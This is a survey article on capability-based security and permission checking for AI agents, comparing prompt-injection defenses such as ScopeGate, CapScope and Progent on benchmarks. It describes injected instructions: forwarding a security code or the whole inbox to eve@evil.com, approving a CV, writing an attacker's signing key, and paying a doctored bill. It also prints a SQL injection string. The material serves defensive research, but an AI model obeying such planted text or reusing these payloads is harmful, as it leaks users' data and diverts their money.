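# Capability-based security for AI agents and the detection of dangerous permission combinations

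## AI agents, injected instructions and ways of granting access

Capability-based security controls what a program can do by controlling which references it holds. A capability is an unforgeable reference that both names a resource, such as a file or a mailbox, and grants specified rights to it. A program without a capability to a file cannot even request that file. Jack Dennis and Earl Van Horn described the idea in 1966, and security researchers have a new reason to take it up because of AI agents. An agent is a language model run in a loop where it can call tools and read their results.

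An agent that answers email or pays bills has access to private information and reads text written by strangers. A stranger can put instructions in that text, and if the model follows them, the stranger can use whatever access the agent has. Some designs limit that access. Some tools warn when an agent's permissions form a dangerous combination, and some methods track where each piece of data came from.

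### The agent loop

A language model by itself only produces text. The ordinary software around it, called the harness, turns some of that text into action. The harness sends the model the user's request and a description of each available tool. The model produces either an answer for the user or a tool call, which is a request to run a named function with given arguments. When the model makes a tool call, the harness runs the function and adds the result to the context, which is the text the model works from at its next step. These steps repeat until the task is over.

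*Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* (Narisetty, Kore and colleagues, 2026) describes a short run in which a user asked Qwen2.5-7B, a small model, to count the appointments on May 15 and summarize each. The model requested a calendar function, and the harness returned the day's events. One event's description contained an instruction to forward a Facebook security code to an outside address and then delete the email that held it. The model's context now included both this instruction and the user's request. In this run the model ignored the instruction and reported three appointments.

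With no defense in place, injected instructions succeeded in 19% of the banking cases and 58% of the cases set in the chat program Slack, but in none of the cases set in the office suite that included the calendar. According to the researchers, the banking and Slack attacks succeeded more often because the user's task already had the agent sending money or posting messages, so the agent could carry out the attacker's action along with the user's.

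Many harnesses get their tools through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard by which servers offer tools to agents. Anthropic introduced MCP in 2024. *MCP 2026 changes the rules* (Granados, 2026) describes the arrangement MCP was meant to replace, in which the model suggests steps and a person carries them out one by one. Monthly downloads of MCP's development kits had passed 400 million by July 2026, according to Anthropic's *Bringing MCP 2026-07-28 to Claude* (2026).

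According to the Model Context Protocol's *Tools* (2026) page, the harness requests a server's list of tools and receives a name, a description and a schema of the expected arguments for each. To use a tool, the harness sends its name and arguments, and the server returns a result, often plain text. The model chooses which tools to invoke and when. The specification recommends, but does not require, that a human be able to refuse any call.

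MCP does draw some boundaries. Under the Model Context Protocol's *Architecture* (2026), the host application keeps the full conversation, and no server should be able to read all of it or see into another server. This protects the servers from one another. It does nothing to keep their outputs apart once the host has gathered them for the model, so a stranger's web page from one server and a private record from another can end up in the same context. (MCP documents also use the word "capability", for a feature that a client or server declares it supports. A capability in that sense grants no access to anything.)

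### Why the model cannot be the guard

Prompt injection is an attack in which text takes effect as an instruction against the wishes of whoever set up the system. In direct injection, the attacker types the instruction into the user's turn. In indirect injection, the attacker plants it in content that an agent reads while doing someone else's task. David C, in *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, gives the example of a recruiter whose system scores CVs. An applicant hides a line in the CV telling the model to ignore its earlier instructions and approve the candidate for interview. The applicant needs no access to the system beyond having it read the CV.

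David C, a technical director at Britain's National Cyber Security Centre, wrote the piece because many security professionals assume that injected instructions are a familiar problem. SQL is the language programs use to query databases, and SQL injection is an old attack on websites that build queries by pasting a visitor's input into a template. If the template is `SELECT * FROM users WHERE name = '…'`, with the input going between the quotation marks, a visitor can enter `' OR '1'='1` to close the quotation early. The rest of the input then becomes part of the command. This makes the condition true for every row, so the database returns the whole table.

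Parameterized queries fixed SQL injection. The program sends the database a query with a placeholder where the name will go. The database parses the query before filling in the name. Parsing settles what is command and what is value, so nothing the visitor types can change the query's structure. The method depends on SQL having a grammar that defines where the command ends and the value begins.

Natural language has no grammar that separates instructions from data, and a language model has no parser that enforces such a separation. The developer's instructions, the user's request and the retrieved web page all reach the model as one sequence of tokens (word fragments), and the model predicts what comes next. Developers can put markers around the untrusted part and train the model to give less weight to instructions inside them. But the markers are also tokens, and their effect depends on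 a learned tendency that no mechanism enforces.

Narisetty and colleagues collect several measurements of how strong this tendency is. One group of researchers attacked twelve published defenses that work on or inside the model. The original evaluations of most of these defenses had found almost no successful attacks. Attackers who knew the defense and adapted to it succeeded more than 90% of the time against most of them. For Claude Opus 4.5, an older Anthropic model, the success rate of indirect injection in coding environments rose from 4.7% with one attempt to 33.6% with ten and 63.0% with a hundred.

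These figures do not prove that the separation is impossible. David C writes that injection may never be fully mitigated in the way SQL injection was, while Narisetty and colleagues treat it as settled that the model cannot enforce the boundary. The disagreement matters little to someone designing an agent now, because a model that fails a few percent of the time offers little protection against an attacker who can keep trying. The agent therefore needs protection that does not depend on the model's judgment.

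In *Prompt Injection Remains Unsolved, OWASP Researcher Warns*, Poireault (2026) reports security researcher Ariel Fogel's view that a successful injection used to produce a bad answer and can now set off a chain of real actions. David C proposes treating the model as an "inherently confusable deputy", a phrase that comes from a story about a compiler, rather than thinking of injection as a flaw to patch.

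### A compiler with two sources of authority

In *The Confused Deputy* (1988), Norm Hardy told what he called a nearly true story from Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers. Tymshare kept a compiler in a directory called SYSX, and customers who ran it could name a file to receive debugging output. The staff had also altered the compiler to log customers' use of language features to a file called STAT in the same directory. To let the compiler write to STAT, they gave it a "home files license", which allowed it to write to any file in SYSX.

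SYSX also held the billing records, in a file named BILL. One customer learned the name and gave it as the destination for debugging output. The compiler passed the name to the operating system, which opened the file because the compiler had a license for SYSX. The debugging output overwrote the billing records.

Hardy considered the obvious repairs. The compiler could have refused any name in SYSX, but the directory did not yet have that name when the programmers wrote the output code, and some customer might have had a legitimate reason to write there. It could have refused BILL specifically, but then someone would have had to revise the compiler every time a new sensitive file appeared. The engineers instead added a system call to "switch hats", which let the compiler specify whether a request relied on its own license or on the customer's authority. This solved the compiler's problem,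 but other programs needed more than two hats, and some kinds of authority had nothing to do with files. The last time Hardy wrote down the conditions for opening a file, they contained fourteen "and"s and "or"s.

According to Hardy, the compiler carried authority from two sources and could not keep them apart. This made it a confused deputy, a program that a less privileged party can trick into misusing its privileges. The trick is possible because of ambient authority, which lets a program use a resource merely by naming it, based on who runs the program or what license it has. *Capability Myths Demolished* (Miller, Yee and Shapiro, 2003) defines ambient authority as authority "exercised, but not selected, by its user", and compares it to a world of doors without keys, where each door opens by itself for anyone allowed through. Similarly, a Unix program presents no credential when it asks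 to open a file, and the request simply succeeds or fails.

### The same compiler under lists and under capabilities

The usual way to control access to files is an access-control list, a record attached to each resource of who may use it and how. It is tempting to think that lists and capabilities are two ways of writing down the same facts. Put the people and programs in rows and the resources in columns, and Tymshare's situation looks like this:

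| | STAT | BILL | Customer's debugging file |
|---|---|---|---|
| Customer | none | none | write |
| Compiler, run by the customer | write | write | write |

Permissions can be written as a table with a row for each program and a column for each resource. An access-control list stores the column for one resource, while a capability system stores the row for each program. Miller and colleagues argue that the two approaches are not equivalent, because the table leaves out how a program indicates which resource it wants.

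Under access-control lists, the compiler has to refer to a file by name. A name such as "BILL" carries no rights, and anyone can type it. The operating system looks up the file, finds that the compiler may write to it, and allows the write. The customer supplied the name, and the compiler wrote to the file using the right Tymshare had given it.

Removing permissions from a program limits the damage it can do, but the program can still be tricked into misusing the permissions it needs. If Tymshare had withdrawn the compiler's access to BILL and left only its access to STAT, which it needed, a customer could still have ruined the statistics by naming STAT as the debugging file. Hardy mentions the need to protect STAT only in a parenthesis, but it is the part of the story that applies best to agents.

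In a capability system, Tymshare gives the compiler a reference to STAT at installation, and the customer passes it a reference to the debugging file instead of the file's name. The compiler writes statistics through the first reference and debugging output through the second. A customer with no right to BILL has no reference to it to pass, and so cannot make the malicious request.

Miller and Shapiro's *Paradigm Regained* illustrates both styles with two ordinary Unix commands that copy one file to another. `cp foo.txt bar.txt` gives the program `cp` two strings. To turn them into files, `cp` must be able to open anything the user might name, so it needs all the user's authority over files. With `cat < foo.txt > bar.txt`, the shell opens both files and passes `cat` two file descriptors, which are references to those open files only. `cat` needs no other access to do this job, although on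 an ordinary system it has the user's full access anyway.

Capabilities do not prevent every confused deputy problem. Miller and colleagues imagine a program that tries each key on a ring until one opens the door, which has the same problem as Hardy's compiler. To avoid this, a deputy has to keep track of what each capability is for.

### How references spread

A capability system also needs rules for how a program comes to hold a reference in the first place. In the object-capability model, programs, files and services are all objects, and one object can affect another only by sending a message along a reference that it holds. There are four ways to obtain a reference:

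- By initial conditions: the object already holds the reference when the system starts.
- By parenthood: an object that creates another receives the only reference to the new one.
- By endowment: the new object starts with those of its creator's references that the creator chooses to give it.
- By introduction: an object that holds references to two others can send one of them a reference to the other.

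In the repaired Tymshare system, the compiler gets STAT by endowment and the customer's debugging file by introduction. A program cannot gain access by guessing a name or looking one up in a public directory. Miller and Shapiro summarize the consequence as "only connectivity begets connectivity", which means that if no chain of references joins two groups of objects, none can ever form. A reviewer who knows nothing about a program's code can therefore draw the references as a graph and find an outer limit on what the program could ever reach.

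Within that limit, information can still travel indirectly. Miller and Shapiro distinguish permission, which covers what a program can do to objects it holds directly, from authority, which includes the effects it can bring about through others. A program with no permission to read the password file still has authority to read it if another program will pass on the contents. Leaks from agents usually happen this way, with the agent reading a message and sending the text to an outsider who never gains access to the mailbox.

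### Least privilege and the reference monitor

Jerome Saltzer and Michael Schroeder set out the principle of least privilege in 1975, which says that every program should run with the smallest set of privileges its task requires. Miller and Shapiro illustrate the opposite with Solitaire, which needs a window, the player's clicks and perhaps one file for saved games, but can read all the player's email on common desktop systems.

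According to Miller and colleagues, the principle requires both the resources and the units that receive access to be small, down to single files and one run of one program. An agent that works under its user's account meets neither requirement, since it has the same access whether it is summarizing a web page or filing a tax return. Even a short list of permissions can be unsafe, because a few tools are enough to assemble the "lethal trifecta" of private data, untrusted content and a way to send data out.

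Something has to enforce the limits the designer picks. James Anderson's 1972 report for the US Air Force described a reference monitor, a component that checks every access against a policy. The programs it controls must not be able to bypass or alter it, and it must be small enough for people to verify. In an agent, the natural place for it is the point where the harness turns a tool call into an action.

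Narisetty and colleagues use the requirements as a list of ways a monitor can fail. A side channel lets information out without any access for the monitor to check. A monitor whose policy comes from a language model is hard to verify, because nobody can inspect a model as they would a short program. Poireault reports a case of tampering from Fogel's talk, in which an agent's output redefined the boundaries of its own sandbox. Fogel also described attacks that an allow-list made easier, because the commands the attacker needed were already approved. In those attacks, the monitor enforced its policy correctly, but the policy was too coarse to stop them.

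### Strings in a shared context

A monitor at the tool boundary sees a function's name and its arguments, which are mostly strings such as email addresses, file paths and account numbers. An agent is like `cp` in Miller and Shapiro's comparison, which also receives file names as strings.

A Model Context Protocol (MCP) server can store state between calls and give the model an identifier, or handle, for it. A shopping server, for example, might create a basket and return the identifier `bsk_a1b2c3`, which the model then repeats in each call that adds an item. For servers that authenticate their callers, the MCP specification describes such a handle as "a name, not a capability", and advises the server to check on every call that the caller may use it. MCP's *Security Best Practices* also forbid servers to treat possession of a handle as authentication. A server that does not authenticate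 callers can check only the string, so the specification recommends one that is hard to guess and soon expires. Such a handle is closer to a capability, but it is still text, and the model can copy it anywhere text can go, including into a message to a stranger.

Checking the caller's identity does not catch an injection, because the caller is the right one. For example, an agent may be entitled to send mail for its user but take the recipient's address from a stranger's message. The call looks the same as it would if the user had supplied the address.

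In Hardy's compiler, the name STAT was part of the program and the name of the debugging file arrived separately as an argument, so a programmer could replace each name with its own capability. An agent's context combines the user's request and the stranger's text in one sequence, and the model generates every argument from the whole sequence. A harness can limit what an attacker can name by giving the model references to choose from instead of letting it write free strings. However, the model still selects which reference to use for each purpose, and the stranger's text can influence that selection.

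David C relays a rule from an online exchange between Baibhav Bista and Simon Willison, the developer who named prompt injection in 2022. Under this rule, when a model processes information from a party, its privileges drop to that party's. An agent reading a stranger's email could then do only what the stranger could do. The rule would stop many attacks, but it would also block a lot of ordinary work. For example, a user who asks an agent to read an email and add any meeting request to the calendar wants the sender's text to determine what goes into the calendar.

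## Checking every tool call against permissions the model cannot change

Before a task starts, a harness can limit an agent by choosing which tools to describe to the model. When the model later requests one of those tools, the harness can check the arguments and decide whether to carry out the request. For example, it might give a support agent a refund tool, then decide whether to allow each refund based on the amount and the customer receiving it.

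Mellafe Zuvic (2026), in *Capability Gates Are Not Authorization*, calls the first control "capability gating" and the second "per-call authorization". "Capability" here means only a tool available to the agent. Gating is useful because an agent with no payment tool cannot pay anyone. But an agent whose job is to make payments needs the tool, and gating does not restrict whom it pays. Tymshare's compiler had the same problem with STAT, the file it did need. Argument schemas do not help much either, because a schema can require an account number to be a string of the right form, but the attacker's account number also has that form.

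### What three frameworks check by default

In June 2026 Mellafe Zuvic, an independent security researcher, published an audit of the public source code of three products. LangChain (with its companion LangGraph) and LlamaIndex are libraries for building agents, and the Stripe Agent Toolkit connects agents to the payment company Stripe. Zuvic found that, by default, none of the three has a step that checks the argument values in a model's tool call against a policy before the tool runs and refuses calls that violate it.

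LangChain looks up the tool named in the model's output in a table and runs it with the model's arguments, usually after validating their structure. Developers can attach callbacks, but these observe calls and cannot reliably stop them. Developers can also add a step in which a person approves calls, but there is none by default. LlamaIndex works in much the same way. If the model names a tool that does not exist, the framework reports this to the model but raises no security alert.

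Stripe's toolkit has two coarse controls, a list of permitted actions and an access key that the developer can restrict to certain kinds of operation. Within those limits, it passes on whatever amount, currency, customer and redirect address the model supplies. The audit covered only public code, and Stripe's remote server may check more. Mellafe Zuvic does not report this as a vulnerability. The frameworks leave authorization to the developer, which is dangerous when the developer assumes the framework handles it.

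Models differ widely in how often they produce bad calls. In a companion test of 27 models, injections presented a harmful call as a necessary part of the user's task. The twelve inexpensive models attempted the call 60% of the time on average, compared with 19% for the fifteen flagship models. The scenarios were short and all came from one author, so the gap between the groups is more informative than either figure.

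### A payout request at ScopeGate

Mellafe Zuvic's remedy, ScopeGate, is a small program that sits between the model and the tools. The demonstration used a merchant's agent with a tool that changes the account that receives the merchant's money. A fixed call, `update_payout_account(account=acct_ATTACKER_999)`, replaced the model's output to simulate a successful injection and make the run repeatable. LangChain's default code ran the call, and the mock payment system recorded the attacker's account.

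ScopeGate puts the same call through a series of checks:

1. **Scope.** The policy must list the tool. It lists `update_payout_account`, so the call continues.
2. **Authorization.** Each constrained argument must have a value from its approved set. The set for `account` contains only `acct_MERCHANT_001`, so ScopeGate denies the call here and the tool never runs.
3. **Money ceiling.** For payments and refunds, the amount must be a finite number between zero and a stated maximum.
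4. **Idempotency.** Some tools require a key that lets the payment system recognize a repeated request. The key must come from trusted software and not from the model.

Only a call that passes every check runs, and an error in any check counts as a denial.

The second check works because the injection cannot change the approved set. The system's operators write the set, and under ScopeGate's rules no model output may contribute to it, even at the drafting stage. If the model could add accounts to the set, the text that corrupted the call could corrupt the set too. The drawback is that a merchant who has really changed banks is also refused until someone updates the set by another route.

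Mellafe Zuvic tried 48 prepared ways around ScopeGate's checks, including invisible characters, lookalike letters, arguments of the wrong type and malformed amounts. None worked on the final version. An earlier prototype had let through the value NaN ("not a number") because testing whether NaN is greater than the maximum returns false. In a second test, the model GLM-5.2 played the attacker for 40 rounds and received the reason for each denial. ScopeGate denied all 29 unauthorized calls the model produced and allowed its two harmless ones. The model also produced nine malformed outputs. In a control test, ScopeGate allowed all ten legitimate calls.

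These zeros are roughly what we would expect from code that compares a string with a set of one member. The tests are good at finding programming errors such as the NaN bug, but we learn less from them about work where nobody can list the acceptable values beforehand.

### One task, several sets of permissions

Coding agents read and write many files and run shell commands, and the files they need access to depend on the bug. *Authority Is Not a String* (Bouras, Dai and Mechtaev, 2026) begins with a case that no single list of permissions can handle.

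A developer asks a coding agent to fix the failing tests in an authentication module. An orchestrator, the agent that divides up the work, gives the test run to a second agent (the runner) and the source edit to a third (the patcher). An attacker has planted a fixture, a piece of supporting test code, that prints an official-looking message among the test results. According to the message, the signing key has changed, and writing a new key into `src/auth/keys.py` will restore the build. The attacker supplied the new key and could use it to forge login tokens.

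The request looks normal because it targets an ordinary source file in a directory that the repair has to change. A policy for the whole task must therefore allow writes to that directory, and if all the agents share the policy, the runner that has just read the message can write there too.

CapScope, the authors' system, gives each agent its own permissions. It calls them capabilities, and defines one as a pair

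$$\mathrm{Cap}[e, \varphi]$$

where $e$ is an effect type and $\varphi$ is a scope predicate, a test that returns true or false for the arguments of a call. There are three effect types: Read, Write and Exec (running a command). A capability covers a call if the tool has that effect type and the arguments pass the test.

For Read and Write, the test resolves any links and `..` steps in the path, then checks that the resulting file lies under a permitted directory. For Exec, it splits a compound command into parts and checks that each part begins with a permitted sequence of words, so permission to run `pytest` does not extend to `pytest && curl`. Inspection commands, such as `grep` and `ls`, always pass.

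The harness keeps a separate store of capabilities for each agent, outside the text that the models read. Three rules govern the stores.

**MINT** creates authority. Before the agent reads any file, a separate model call uses the user's request and the project's file names to predict what the task will need. Ordinary code validates the prediction and freezes it as $D$, the ceiling on authority for the whole task.

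**DERIVE** hands part of that authority to another agent. When the orchestrator delegates a subtask, it requests a set of capabilities $C'$ for the sub-agent. The harness installs only those that fit within the ceiling:

$$C'' = \{\, c' \in C' : c' \preceq c \ \text{for some}\ c \in D \,\}$$

Here $c' \preceq c$ means that $c'$ and $c$ have the same effect type and that any arguments passing the test of $c'$ also pass the test of $c$. For example, write access to `src/**` (everything under `src`) can be narrowed to `src/parser.py`, but access to that file can never be expanded to the whole directory.

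**INVOKE** runs a tool. If the calling agent's store has a capability that covers the call, the harness runs the tool and adds the output to the context. Otherwise, the model receives a refusal.

Only MINT adds authority, and it acts before the agent has read any file or command output. File names are visible at this point, but the paper does not consider attacks through them. A deployment can let a user approve an extra capability later, which counts as a new MINT, but this option was turned off in the experiments.

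In the signing-key case, the ceiling allows reading the project, writing under `src`, and running `pytest` and a type checker. The runner may only read the tests and run `pytest`. When it runs the tests, the planted message enters its context, and the model issues a call to write the new key. The harness rejects the call because the runner's store has no Write capability. The patcher can still fix the bug.

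The attacker still has two ways to get the key changed. The runner may pass the request to the orchestrator, which could then ask the patcher to make the edit. More directly, the fixture could write the file itself, since it is code that `pytest` executes. CapScope does not control what a permitted command does once it is running, and leaves that to a sandbox around the process.

### Three hundred repairs

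Bouras and colleagues tested CapScope on five small Python projects, each with one bug and a failing test suite. They planted instructions in five places: the README, AGENTS.md (a file of agent instructions that the harness loads automatically), a skill file (a reusable set of agent instructions), a source comment and the test output. Each called for a plausible action that the repair did not need, such as running one of the project's own utilities. They tested every combination of project, place and four kinds of permission three times, for a total of 300 runs, all on the model Qwen3.5-Flash. Every run used an orchestrator, a runner, a patcher and a verifier that repeated the tests, so the conditions differed only in their permissions.

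| Permissions | Injected action carried out | Bug repaired | Mean time |
|---|---|---|---|
| No restriction | 47 of 75 | 72 of 75 | 145 s |
| One fixed list of forbidden actions | 46 of 75 | 70 of 75 | 140 s |
| One policy written for the task, shared by all agents | 33 of 75 | 68 of 75 | 194 s |
| CapScope | 3 of 75 | 68 of 75 | 316 s |

The fixed list forbade well-known dangerous operations, such as deleting directories or reading password files, but it made almost no difference because the injections relied on ordinary operations. A policy written for the task helped more, but it had to give every agent all the permissions that any of them needed. Under CapScope, the model still attempted the injected action in 34 of the 75 runs, so the low figure in the table is mainly due to the harness refusing those calls.

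All three successful attacks on CapScope came through AGENTS.md. CapScope describes two ways an injection can still succeed. A sub-agent may receive more than its subtask needs, such as a whole directory instead of one file. Or the injected text may influence how the orchestrator describes the subtask, so that the sub-agent receives the permission the attacker wants. In both cases the action lies within the ceiling, so INVOKE allows it.

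CapScope failed to complete seven repairs. Two failed because the initial prediction left out write access that the patcher needed. In another two, the runner worked out the right edit, but the edit never reached the patcher. The last three ended with passing tests but exceeded the 15-minute limit. In many of the slow runs, the agent repeatedly tried the same forbidden action because no person was there to tell it to stop. The initial prediction would be harder to get right for a large migration, where it is difficult to tell from file names what the work will involve, than it was for these one-bug projects.

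### Why CapScope is not an object-capability system

CapScope's model writes a path such as `src/auth/keys.py` as a string, and the harness checks a table to see whether the agent may use it. In an object-capability system, a program acts only through references, so Bouras and colleagues instead classify CapScope as a reference monitor on the host.

The distinction matters most for the patcher. Suppose it has write access to everything under `src` to fix one file. An injected instruction, perhaps in a comment in the code it is editing, can tell it to write to the key file, and the harness will allow the write. The patcher is then a confused deputy like Hardy's compiler, though with less authority. In an object-capability design, the orchestrator would give the patcher a reference to the one file it has to fix, and the patcher could not ask for another. CapScope comes close to this when the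 orchestrator narrows a grant to a single path, but it does not require the orchestrator to do so. CapScope does take from the capability tradition the practice of delegating less authority than one holds.

### Progent's rules for individual calls

CapScope sets the agent's maximum permissions before the task begins. For some tasks, though, the permissions needed only become clear after the agent has read something. *Progent* (Shi, He and colleagues, 2025) allows the rules to change during the task, subject to a check.

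A Progent policy is a list of rules. Each rule allows or forbids one tool under stated conditions on its arguments. A condition can compare numbers, test whether a value is on a list, or match a text pattern. For each call, Progent checks the rules for that tool, starting with those that forbid it. The first rule whose conditions hold determines whether the call is allowed. If no rule applies, Progent blocks the call. A rule can also specify whether Progent responds to a blocked call by stopping the agent, asking the user, or sending the model an error message so that it can try something else.

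In the paper's example, a user asks an agent to carry out the tasks in an email from Alice. The first policy allows only a search for that email. Alice asks in the email for a summary of the user's recent mail to be posted to the user's Slack account, so a second policy adds tools for reading mail, looking up the account and posting. Once the agent learns that the account is called `alice`, a third policy restricts Slack messages to that recipient. One of the recent emails contains an instruction to forward the whole inbox to `eve@evil.com`. If the agent obeys and requests `send_email`, Progent blocks the call because no rule allows it. The agent then posts the summary.

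A language model writes these policies, and to update them it reads the results of tool calls, which can include the attacker's text. Progent therefore treats each new policy as a proposal. Let $A(P)$ be the set of all calls that policy $P$ allows. A proposed policy $P'$ takes effect automatically only if

$$A(P') \subseteq A(P)$$

which means that it allows nothing that the current policy does not. Progent checks this with an SMT solver, a program that determines whether a set of logical conditions can hold together. The solver looks for a call that the new policy would allow and the old one would not. If such a call exists, the update is an expansion and needs approval. Shi and colleagues call the resulting guarantee "monotonic confinement": between approvals, the set of permitted calls can only shrink.

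The solver can detect an expansion, but it cannot determine whether the user would want it. Alice's email prompts the addition of the Slack tools, and the attacker's email prompts the addition of `send_email`. Both are expansions prompted by text that someone other than the user wrote. *Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) lists among Progent's limitations that hostile tool results may lead an update to relax the rules. The solver prevents this from happening silently, but the outcome depends on the person or system that answers the request for approval.

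Each Progent rule also checks one call by itself, so the policy must be rewritten to use a value learned during the task. *Trident* (2026), a later design, uses policies that account for the order of events. For example, a policy can save the sender of an email when the agent reads it, then allow a reply only to that sender.

### Progent's results on AgentDojo

The usual test for such systems is AgentDojo, a set of simulated applications with 97 user tasks and, in the original paper, *AgentDojo* (2024), 629 security cases that each combine a user's task with an attacker's goal. *Assessing Automated Prompt Injection Attacks in Agentic Environments* (2026) describes the applications as covering office work, banking, travel and Slack, with the attacker's text placed where a stranger's text would naturally appear, such as an email body. After each run, ordinary code checks whether, for example,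 money was transferred or a message was sent in the simulation, so no model has to judge the result. Researchers report the attack success rate alongside utility, the share of users' tasks that the agent completes.

Shi and colleagues tested Progent with GPT-4o as the agent. On AgentDojo, 39.9% of attacks succeeded without Progent and 1.0% with it. On another benchmark, Agent Security Bench, the rate fell from 70.3% to 3.9%. Utility stayed about the same on both. Most of the attacks that still succeeded on Agent Security Bench used tools whose names and descriptions closely resembled those of legitimate tools, and hand-written rules stopped these attacks.

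In these headline tests, Progent approved every expansion automatically, to imitate a user who clicks yes to everything. The guarantee of monotonic confinement therefore contributed nothing to the low figures, which show that the benchmark's injections seldom misled the model writing the policies. That is encouraging, but it again depends on how a model behaves. Attack success on AgentDojo also depended on how updates were handled. It was 2.5% with updates switched off, so that the only policy came from the user's own request. It was zero with a person reviewing every policy, though the researchers assumed a reviewer with strong security awareness. Only 6% of updates were expansions, so the reviewer's workload would have been light.

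Progent cannot stop an attack that needs only permitted calls, or one whose payload is text for the user to read. Shi and colleagues therefore left out two AgentDojo attacks that steer the agent toward a different but legitimate hotel.

### Why a fixed set of attacks misled earlier work

AgentDojo's attacks predate the defenses that researchers test on it and do not adapt to them. Narisetty and colleagues argue that testing against fixed attacks led the field to trust injection detectors that did not deserve it. A detector can score well by learning the features of familiar attack strings. Its developers then report the score as resistance to attackers, when they have measured resistance to one collection of text. The main example is the twelve defenses mentioned earlier, which attackers broke in *The Attacker Moves Second* (2025). Narisetty and colleagues also cite a detector called Attention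 Tracker, which scored perfectly on standard benchmarks by one common measure. On another dataset it missed 69% of injections, and all of them once the attacker added a few separator characters.

Ma, Li and colleagues (2026) describe such a failure in *AutoDojo*. A user asks a banking agent to pay the bill in a file. AgentDojo's standard injection adds a message to the file instructing the AI assistant to send money to the attacker first. PIGuard, a classifier trained to detect injections, removes the suspicious sentences and the attack fails. The AutoDojo version is a plausible bill with a small fee, the attacker's account number and a notice that the payment details have changed. It contains no command. PIGuard passes the file on unchanged, and the agent pays the attacker.

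AutoDojo found such texts automatically. Over six rounds, a language model received the success rate of earlier attempts, inferred what kind of defense might be in place and wrote a new version. It had no other access to the agent or the defense. With an agent running GPT-4o-mini, this raised the success rate against PIGuard from 0% to 28.0%.

Narisetty and colleagues warn that the reputation of systems such as Progent rests on the same kind of benchmark. The counterargument is that a check on tool calls does not process the attacker's text, so rewording an email may fool a classifier but cannot give a call to `send_email` the permission it lacks. To beat such a check, the attacker has to corrupt the policy or achieve the goal through calls that the policy already allows. That should be harder, but experiments are needed to show whether it is hard enough.

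### Adaptive tests of Progent

Shi and colleagues ran the first such tests themselves. They added text telling the policy model to allow every tool, tried a milder reminder to update the permissions, and used an automated search for effective injections. Approval was again automatic, and the attacks succeeded only slightly more often.

In June 2026 Narisetty and colleagues repeated the exercise using Qwen2.5-7B, the small model from the appointments example, both to run the agent and to write the policies. They used the first eight user tasks from three of AgentDojo's four applications and ran everything three times. Their adaptive attack described the malicious action as a routine step that was already authorized, hoping the policy model would add the necessary permission.

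| | No defense | Progent, standard attack | Progent, adaptive attack |
|---|---|---|---|
| Banking: attack success | 19.0% | 1.9% | 3.7% |
| Slack: attack success | 58.3% | 10.8% | 4.2% |
| Office work: attack success | 0% | 0% | 0% |
| Mean attack success | 25.8% | 4.2% | 2.6% |
| Mean utility under attack | 45.2% | 27.1% | 25.8% |

Progent reduced attack success, but the averages need careful interpretation. The office tasks add nothing to the comparison, since no attack succeeded there even without a defense. In Slack, the share of tasks the agent completed fell from 47.5% to 20.8% with Progent on, so some attacks may have failed there because the agent could do less overall. The banking results are clearer evidence, because attack success fell by nine tenths while the share of tasks completed stayed at 31.9%. Progent also needed about fifteen times as many model calls per task.

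Oddly, the adaptive attack did worse than the standard one. Narisetty and colleagues suspect that the milder wording, which they chose to reassure the policy model, also made the agent less likely to obey. If so, the 2.6% partly reflects a weak attack. Although one successful template would have been enough to show that the defense can break, the failure of this one doesn't show that a better attack would fail.

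A small model may write worse policies than GPT-4o would, which makes Progent's success more impressive. But it may also fail to carry out an attack that a stronger agent would complete, which could make Progent look more effective than it is. The small variation across the three runs shows that the result is repeatable in this setting, but not that it would hold for other models or attacks.

AutoDojo provides some of the missing evidence. Ma and colleagues tested five models and optimized the attack over several rounds. With GPT-4o-mini as the agent, attack success against Progent was 8.2% for the standard injection and 7.7% for the optimized ones. With two of the other models, it was about two percentage points higher for the optimized injections. These figures are probably too low, because the researchers saved money by optimizing the attacks against a version of Progent with a different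 policy model from the one in the final test. Even so, the contrast with PIGuard supports the view that checking calls holds up better than detecting suspicious text.

Fixed benchmarks can also make a defense look more usable than it is. Li, Wen and colleagues (2026) point out in *AgentDyn* that only 6 of AgentDojo's 97 tasks require the agent to change its plan based on what it finds. They wrote 60 tasks that all require this, with more tools and with helpful instructions in outside content, such as a request to log in before checking out. On these tasks, GPT-4o completed 53.3% with no defense and 6.7% with Progent. Li and colleagues found that Progent had trouble assigning the right permissions when there were many tools, and that the errors accumulated until it blocked almost everything useful. Attack success was only 1.7%, but an agent that can do so little also gives attacks little chance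 to succeed.

None of these experiments isolates an attack that uses only calls the policy already permits, which Narisetty and colleagues consider the most important attack left to try. The altered bill suggests how such an attack might work. The user has asked the agent to pay whatever account the file names, so the policy must allow that payment for the agent to do its job. If an attacker has changed the account number, a rule that checks only the tool and its arguments cannot detect the change.

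## Granting, delegating and revoking an agent's permissions

A harness that checks tool calls needs a policy, which may be written by an operator, a model or the user. The choice of author affects whether an attacker's text can influence the rules. The right permissions also change during a task. An agent may discover that it needs another file, hand part of the work to a second agent, and finish with the file long before the task ends.

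### Who writes the rules

An operator can write fixed rules before the agent starts. This keeps an attacker's text out of the rules, and it works well when the acceptable values are few and known, as with a merchant's payout account. It works less well for a coding agent, because every request involves different files, and an operator who cannot predict them has to allow whole directories.

A model can write narrower rules for each task. CapScope uses a model to predict the necessary permissions before the agent reads any file, and Progent uses one to revise the rules as results come in. The harness can also ask the user whenever the agent needs a new permission. Designers can combine these methods. In *Dynamic Capability Scoping for Enterprise AI Agents*, Noyan proposes a limit on permissions for each job role, a classifier that takes account of the current task, and bans on certain combinations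 of permissions.

Researchers disagree about whether a model should write any part of the policy. Mellafe Zuvic keeps model output out of ScopeGate's policies because an injection could otherwise corrupt the rules along with the call they are meant to check.

CapScope freezes its prediction before the agent opens any file. A prompt injection can corrupt only what a model writes after reading it, so an instruction hidden in a source comment can't change the prediction.

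This answers the argument when injections arrive in file contents or command output, but the prediction can go wrong in other ways. The predicting model in Bouras and colleagues' system still sees file names, which a repository's contributors choose. Users also paste text from elsewhere into their requests, so even the "trusted" input may contain an attacker's instructions. Mellafe Zuvic considers a model with a backdoor in its weights, where a trigger phrase produces an action the attacker chose. Such a model could write a bad policy from an innocent-looking request. A frozen prediction is a reasonable way to limit a coding agent whose edits someone will review, but a poor way to decide which bank account may receive money.

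### The costs of granting too much or too little

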